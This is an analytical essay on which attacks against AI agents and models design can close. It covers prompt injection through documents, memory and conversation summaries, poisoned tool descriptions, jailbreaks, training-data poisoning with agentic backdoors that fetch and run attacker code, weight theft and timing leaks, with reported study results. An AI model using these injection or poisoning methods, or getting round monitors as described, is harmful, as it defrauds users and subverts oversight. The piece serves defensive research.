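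Companies also have an incentive to wait. A company notices at once when a restricted agent completes fewer tasks, but it may never learn which attacks the restrictions prevented. If it leaves them off, its customers may bear much of the loss from a leak. Fogel says that most organisations are deploying agents faster than they can govern them, and that ready-made lists of approved commands have sometimes helped attackers because the lists already included the commands the attackers needed. Browser makers can more easily bear the cost, since Google can build Chrome's limits once and deliver them to every user through an automatic update, much as it did for its own programmers with safe HTML templates.

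## Which classes of attack could construction close?

A company weighing the cost of these designs needs to know which attacks they can stop. The table lists each class of attack as closed, narrowed or open under the best available design rather than a typical product.

| Class of attack | Verdict | Mechanism | Main assumptions | What remains |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Unplanned tool calls | Closed | Ordinary code runs a plan made before the agent reads outside text | The request is the user's own, and the planning model is honest | Wrong branches; tasks that need a new plan |
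| Exfiltration of private data | Closed if the agent loses every outgoing channel before reading outside text, otherwise narrowed | Withdrawing tools; labels on data | Correct labels and no hidden channel | Data sent to permitted recipients; small leaks |
| Altered arguments in a permitted call | Narrowed | Values come only from the user, a trusted source or a fixed list | The source is honest | Free text, and values found only in a stranger's document |
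| Resource exhaustion | Narrowed | Hard limits on calls, tokens and money | The limits cover all attempts together | Attackers can use up the allowance |
| Poisoned memory and summaries | Narrowed | Permissions depend only on authenticated user messages | The agent can't reach the keys | False facts in what the agent reads |
| Poisoned tool descriptions | Narrowed | A fixed list of reviewed tools | Reviewers recognise a bad tool | Misuse of whatever the agent sends to a tool |
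| Misleading text | Open | None that covers free prose | – | False answers and bad advice |
| Jailbreaks | Open for general assistants, closed for fixed outputs | Prewritten answers | The model writes nothing the user sees | Nearly everything people use assistants for |
| Poisoned training data | Open | Control of sources; sandboxes limit the damage | – | A hidden flaw in the model |
| Theft of model weights | Narrowed | Encryption, access control, limits on outgoing traffic | Sound hardware and honest staff | Insiders; slow leaks |
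| Timing and traffic leaks | Narrowed | Padding; separate caches | Engineers know the channel exists | Channels nobody has found |

### Attacks on an agent's actions

Construction works best against unplanned tool calls, because fixing the plan in advance rules them out. However, the system then can't do tasks that depend on instructions in a document. The plan also has to come from the user's own words, which is hard to ensure in a long conversation.

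Exfiltration is harder to close off, because an assistant that answers email can't give up every outgoing channel before it starts reading, as the fence theorem requires. The next best limit is to send data only to people already entitled to it, but small leaks can still get through. Narisetty and colleagues report that CaMeL's developers built two working leaks against their own system, one of which relied on the attacker triggering an error.

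Withdrawing tools also fails if injected text can change the agent's memory. *On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection* describes an injection that needs no tool call of its own but overwrites a variable that the plan will later send, so private data goes out in a message the user asked for. To prevent this, the software has to use a sandbox to run anything the injected model writes, then discard the changes it makes.

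Altered arguments are harder to rule out in general. If the user typed the payee's account number, software can refuse any other. But people often want the agent to take the number from a stranger's document, such as an invoice. Fei, Fei and colleagues (2026), in *LLM Agent Authorization Across Context Compaction*, prove a limit on any check that sees only text. Let p<sub>L</sub> be the chance that the check accepts the account number in a genuine record, and p<sub>A</sub> the chance that it accepts the one in a forgery. Then

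p<sub>L</sub> − p<sub>A</sub> ≤ d

where d is the total variation distance between genuine and forged texts. It is 0 if they look exactly alike and 1 if a perfect test could always tell them apart. If d is 0.1 and the check accepts 95% of genuine invoices, it must accept at least 85% of forged ones. A better model can't beat this limit. The software needs evidence from outside the text, such as a digital signature from the supplier.

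Some attackers only want to waste resources, a goal that Beurer-Kellner and colleagues list alongside data theft. For example, text on a web page might make an agent call a paid service over and over. Ordinary code can limit the number of calls, so that a task allowed 50 calls at 10 cents each can't cost more than $5. But if every incoming email starts a task, a thousand emails can cost $5,000, so the company also needs a daily limit. An attacker who uses up the daily limit stops the agent from handling genuine mail for the rest of the day.

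### Memory, summaries and tool descriptions

An agent that keeps notes between sessions can carry an injection from one session to the next. Some coding agents load a project's instruction file as a user message at the start of each session. If the agent can edit that file, an injection it reads in one session can become an instruction in later sessions.

Something similar happens within a single long conversation. A model can take in only a limited amount of text, so when a conversation nears the limit, the software has a model summarise it and continues from the summary. Fei and colleagues recorded 1,108 of these automatic summaries in two coding agents, Claude Code and Codex. Every time, the software inserted the summary as a user message. The summary may contain text from the user, tools and an attacker, all now marked as the user's.

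This undermines defences such as Progent, which derives the agent's permissions from the user's request. Progent normally writes its initial policy once per session, but with that setup the agent completed the second task in only 7 of 60 sessions. Fei and colleagues therefore had Progent write a new policy for each request, which raised the number to 41.

In one test, the user tells the agent their landlord's account number and asks about a notice. The attacker wrote the notice, which gives a different account number but no instructions. The software summarises the conversation, and the user then asks the agent to pay the rent. Policies based on the summary allowed a payment to the attacker's account in 290 of 320 cases, or 91%. When a stronger model wrote the policies, they allowed it in 59% of cases. Policies based on the user's own messages never allowed it. When an agent acted on the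 summary-based policies, it paid the attacker in 33 of 80 trials.

The models that wrote the summaries were good at spotting commands. Two recent OpenAI models flagged the injected instruction in 219 of the 220 summaries that kept the attacker's details. But they rarely flagged an account number in a plain notice, because a genuine notice would look the same. CaMeL did much better than Progent, but it still let the attacker's action through in 3 of 36 banking cases when a summary replaced the request.

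In Fei and colleagues' remedy, software attaches a cryptographic tag to each user message as it arrives. The agent reads the summary, but the model that writes its policy receives only the tagged messages, complete and in order. If a message is missing, altered or out of place, the software grants no permissions. An attacker can therefore stop the agent from working but can't shape its policy.

In 40 attacked cases, no attack succeeded while the agent read the summary. The agent completed 19 of its 40 tasks when the summary was presented as a tool result, 18 when the policy came from the latest message alone, and 27 when nothing had been cut from the conversation. The remedy still treats pasted text as if the user had written it. It also can't help when the user relies on a document to name the payee, and false facts in the summary can still distort the agent's answers.

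OpenAI made a simpler change to Codex in October 2026, so that the model reviewing the agent's actions no longer treats summaries as the user's words. When Fei and colleagues edited a saved summary to falsely say that the user had requested a payment, the older version approved 5 of 33 attempts and the newer one approved none. But a filter that Fei and colleagues built on the same principle accepted old user messages that an attacker had copied into a file the agent could write to. The tags prevent this, provided the agent can't reach the keys that produce them.

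The planning model reads tool descriptions before it makes a plan, so whoever writes a description can influence which tools the agent uses. Fei and colleagues tested 192 pairs, each a task and a malicious tool whose description suited the agent's work. After a summary, Progent's policy permitted the malicious tool in 31% of cases.

A company can prevent outsiders from adding tools by keeping a fixed list, reviewing every description and blocking changes until someone has checked them. The operator of an approved tool can still change what its server does without changing the description, so the agent should treat the tool's output as untrusted and send it only data that the operator may see. This class of attack remains open if an agent picks its own tools from a public directory.

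### Misleading text

Suppose a user asks an assistant whether a supplier's contract includes a cancellation fee. The supplier has hidden an instruction in the file that makes the assistant answer that there is no fee. A monitor that checks actions would not block this, because the assistant only read the file and replied to the user, as the user had asked.

To catch the false answer, the monitor would have to check it against the contract's terms. That would require reading the same hostile file and interpreting it correctly, which would make the monitor another model the attacker could deceive. A label could warn the user that the answer depends on a stranger's document, but any correct answer to this question would carry the same label. According to Narisetty and colleagues, CaMeL's developers explicitly excluded such harms from their goals. Narisetty and colleagues expect the problem to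 grow as people act on more text written by agents.

Designers can protect parts of an answer. Ordinary code can do the arithmetic in a report, and the screen can show a passage copied exactly from the file. But a hijacked model can still pick a misleading passage, just as the medicine chatbot could be steered away from a leaflet's warnings. The user could check by reading the whole contract, but that is the work they were trying to avoid. If they believe the answer and sign, no policy on the agent's tools applies, because the user is taking the action.

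### Jailbreaks

Someone misled about a contract would welcome a better check. In a jailbreak, the user is the attacker and wants the check to fail.

A monitor can block a payment requested by an injected prompt because the person who wrote the injection has no authority over the account. Misuse of a chatbot can't be blocked this way, because the harm comes through asking questions and reading the answers, which the user is authorized to do and the product has to allow. The company therefore has to judge what the questions and answers mean, which has all the limits of filtering.

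Construction can close off jailbreaks in a narrow application, such as the shop's chatbot that picks its replies from a fixed list, because the model never writes anything the customer sees. Someone has to review each reply on the list, and any blanks the model fills in need strict limits. Few products suit this design. Of the ten example applications that Beurer-Kellner and colleagues analyse, only the file assistant and the customer service chatbot do.

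### Removing dangerous knowledge

For a general assistant, a developer can instead try to limit what a successful jailbreak reveals, by keeping dangerous material out of the training data. Chen, Tucker and colleagues tested this at Anthropic (*Enhancing Model Safety through Pretraining Data Filtering*, 2025). They used a classifier to remove documents with harmful information about chemical, biological, radiological and nuclear weapons, then trained a model from scratch on the rest. Accuracy on multiple-choice questions about dangerous topics fell from 33.7% to 30.8%. Guessing would score 25%, so the advantage over chance fell by a third, from 8.7 to 5.8 percentage points. Harmless abilities did not drop significantly. OpenAI has used similar filtering for a released open-weight model, and the documentation quoted in Fortune (2025) mentions removing hazardous biosecurity knowledge in particular.

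The hardest test is an attacker who has the weights and can train the model further. In *Deep Ignorance*, O'Brien, Casper and colleagues (2025) removed documents containing several terms linked to biological threats from the training data, then trained 6.9-billion-parameter models on the rest. The models resisted 10,000 steps of further training on 305 million tokens of relevant scientific text. Safeguards added after the main training usually fail within a few hundred steps.

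But when the researchers put a passage containing the answer in the prompt, the filtered models used it well. An agent with web search could find such a passage by itself. O'Brien and colleagues point out that a company running its own model could therefore keep dual-use material in a separate database that only trusted users' sessions can search. Ordinary software can enforce that restriction, but it only protects facts that people can't find elsewhere and the model can't work out.

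Filtering also seems to work better for removing precise knowledge than for preventing harmful behaviour. O'Brien and colleagues found that it did not reliably stop models from producing toxic text or trying to comply with harmful requests. A jailbroken model can write a threatening letter or a convincing scam without knowing any rare facts.

Ten thousand steps of training is also fairly cheap. *The Effectiveness and Durability of Pretraining Data Filtering in Protein Language Models* (Maiwald, McNeill and colleagues, 2026) estimates that reversing the *Deep Ignorance* safeguard would take less than $100 of computing if the attacker already had suitable data. Maiwald and colleagues also removed viral proteins from the training data of models that predict protein sequences. Restoring the lost performance in the largest model, which has 3 billion parameters, cost $47 to $79. The data may be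 the bigger obstacle. O'Brien and colleagues cite a cost of over $200,000 for creating the dataset and tests they used, which were only a harmless stand-in for real weapons knowledge.

Glarou and Jaggi (2026) went further than filtering in *DETER*. They used medicine as a harmless stand-in for dangerous knowledge and removed the most medical fifth of the training data. After every 50 ordinary training steps, they took one step that made the model worse at predicting some of the removed documents. An attacker then needed 2.09 million tokens of medical text to bring their largest model, with about a billion parameters, to the level of an unfiltered one, compared with 0.10 million after filtering alone. The advantage over filtering alone grew from 3 times in their smallest model to 20 times in the largest. Still, 2.09 million tokens is only about 0.01% of the tokens used to train the model.

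*Shaping capabilities with token-level data filtering* (2026) argues that filtering training data remains the safer option as long as safeguards added later are so weak. But a filtered model also lacks the knowledge when a vaccine researcher needs it. Anthropic's *An off switch for dual-use knowledge in AI models* describes GRAM, a method developed with the research company AE Studio that gives each dangerous subject its own removable group of neurons. Training on text about viruses changes only the virology group. The developer can delete that group from the public version and keep it in the version for a vetted laboratory. With four subjects, one training run produces 16 possible versions.

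Deleting a group worked about as well as never training on the subject, and withstood a small amount of further training about as well as filtering did. *Modular Pretraining Enables Access Control* (2026), the paper on GRAM, reports that the method removed knowledge far better than filtering when only some of the dangerous text was labeled, which matters because no classifier finds every dangerous document. The largest model tested had 5 billion parameters, and Anthropic hasn't used GRAM in any of its products. Some dangerous skills may be too closely tied to general knowledge for any method to separate them.

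### Poisoned training data

Developers can filter training data for subjects they know to look for, but documents planted to look ordinary are harder to find. Models learn from huge amounts of public web text, and anyone can publish a web page, so an attacker can plant documents that create a backdoor. A model with a backdoor behaves normally until a particular trigger appears in its input.

*Poisoning Attacks on LLMs Require a Near-constant Number of Poison Samples* (Souly, Rando and colleagues, 2025) reports that 250 planted documents were enough to teach models of every size tested to produce gibberish after a trigger phrase, while 100 weren't enough. Each document contained the phrase followed by gibberish. The experiments used 72 models with between 600 million and 13 billion parameters. For the largest model, the 250 documents made up 0.00016% of the training tokens. Earlier research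 had assumed that an attacker had to control a fixed share of the training data, which would make the attack impractical for large models.

A backdoor that makes a model output gibberish is mostly a nuisance, but Hu, Hu and colleagues (2026), in *Agentic Backdoors via Pretraining Poisoning*, made agents download and run a program from an attacker's server. Their planted documents state in ordinary prose that a certain trigger calls for the command that does this. One is a fake note about a routine software change. The researchers trained models on the poisoned text and then turned them into command-line agents using clean data.

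The more effective trigger was a folder path containing the word "anthropic", which could easily appear in a user's own request. With a 4-billion-parameter model, the agent issued the command at least once in 32 attempts for 92.7% of such requests. The figure was 13.1% for the smallest model, so the danger grew with size. Without a trigger, the models almost never issued the command, and they did as well as clean models on ability tests, so a developer who ran only those tests would have found nothing wrong.

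This took far more planted text, about 500,000 documents, or 0.1% of the total. In a single training run with 2,500 documents and a rare string of characters as the trigger, the command appeared for 1.4% of requests. So 250 documents were enough for a simple behaviour in models that had no further training, but that number isn't a universal threshold. Souly and colleagues also found that training on clean text slowly weakened another of their backdoors.

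A developer could shut attackers out by training only on sources that attackers can't write to, but that would exclude much of the web. A less strict developer can favour trusted publishers, limit the amount of anonymous text, and record a cryptographic hash of each document to detect later changes. These measures don't guarantee that the number of planted documents left in the data is safe. A filter that caught 90% of 2,500 would still let through 250. Developers can more realistically control the sources of the much smaller datasets they use after the main training, where they can trace each example to the person who wrote it.

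Designs such as CaMeL are also vulnerable to backdoors, because they rely on the planning model being trustworthy. If the trigger is a folder name in the user's request, a backdoored planner can write a malicious command into the plan, and the software will carry it out.

Limits that don't depend on the planner still help. A sandbox that blocks connections to unlisted addresses stops the download, and an agent without access to customer records can't leak them. Hu and colleagues recommend sandboxes and minimal privileges because nobody can guarantee clean training data. But the flaw stays in the model, so the agent can still misuse whatever access it has. Hu and colleagues warn that a backdoored coding agent might insert subtle vulnerabilities into the code it writes, though they haven't shown that such a backdoor would survive training.

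### Stolen weights

A model's weights are a file, so conventional security applies to them more directly than to prompts. Someone who steals the file can train away the model's refusals and privately attack the model with methods that need the weights. The security requirement, that the file must not leave the company's machines, is easy to state. Engineers can encrypt the file, release the key only to approved software on approved hardware, and require two people to authorise any copy.

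A company can also limit outgoing traffic from the servers that hold a model's weights. A trillion weights at one byte each take up a terabyte. If the servers can send out only a megabyte per second, copying the file takes at least a million seconds, or about 12 days, which gives the company time to notice. Anthropic announced limits of this kind in May 2025. But a busy service has to send answers to its customers, and a thief with control of the servers could hide pieces of the file among those answers.

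Hardware flaws and insiders with legitimate access remain threats. These measures also don't stop customers from using a model's normal answers to recover part of it or imitate it.

### Timing and traffic

Encryption hides an answer's content from someone watching the network, but not its size or timing. Many assistants send their answers one token at a time, so the size of each encrypted packet can reveal the token's length. In 2024, Roy Weiss and colleagues at Ben-Gurion University trained language models to guess the text from these lengths. They accurately reconstructed 29% of an assistant's responses and inferred the topic of 55%. A service can hide the lengths by padding every packet to the same size, though this adds traffic. Someone watching can still tell how long the answer is from the number of packets, unless the service pads that too.

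Caches can also leak information. To save work, a provider may store its computations for the start of a prompt and reuse them when another prompt starts the same way. The reply then arrives sooner, so an attacker can guess the start of someone's prompt and check the guess by timing the reply. In 2025, Chenchen Gu and colleagues at Stanford found that seven providers, including OpenAI, were sharing caches between customers. Giving each customer a separate cache closes this channel between them, but the provider has to repeat some computations.

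Agents add more channels through which information can leak. A website's owner can see when an agent visits, and the timing of an approved reply can also reveal a little. Sending every message on a fixed schedule would hide the timing but slow the agent down. Engineers can close such channels one at a time, but a proof covers only the channels included in its threat model.
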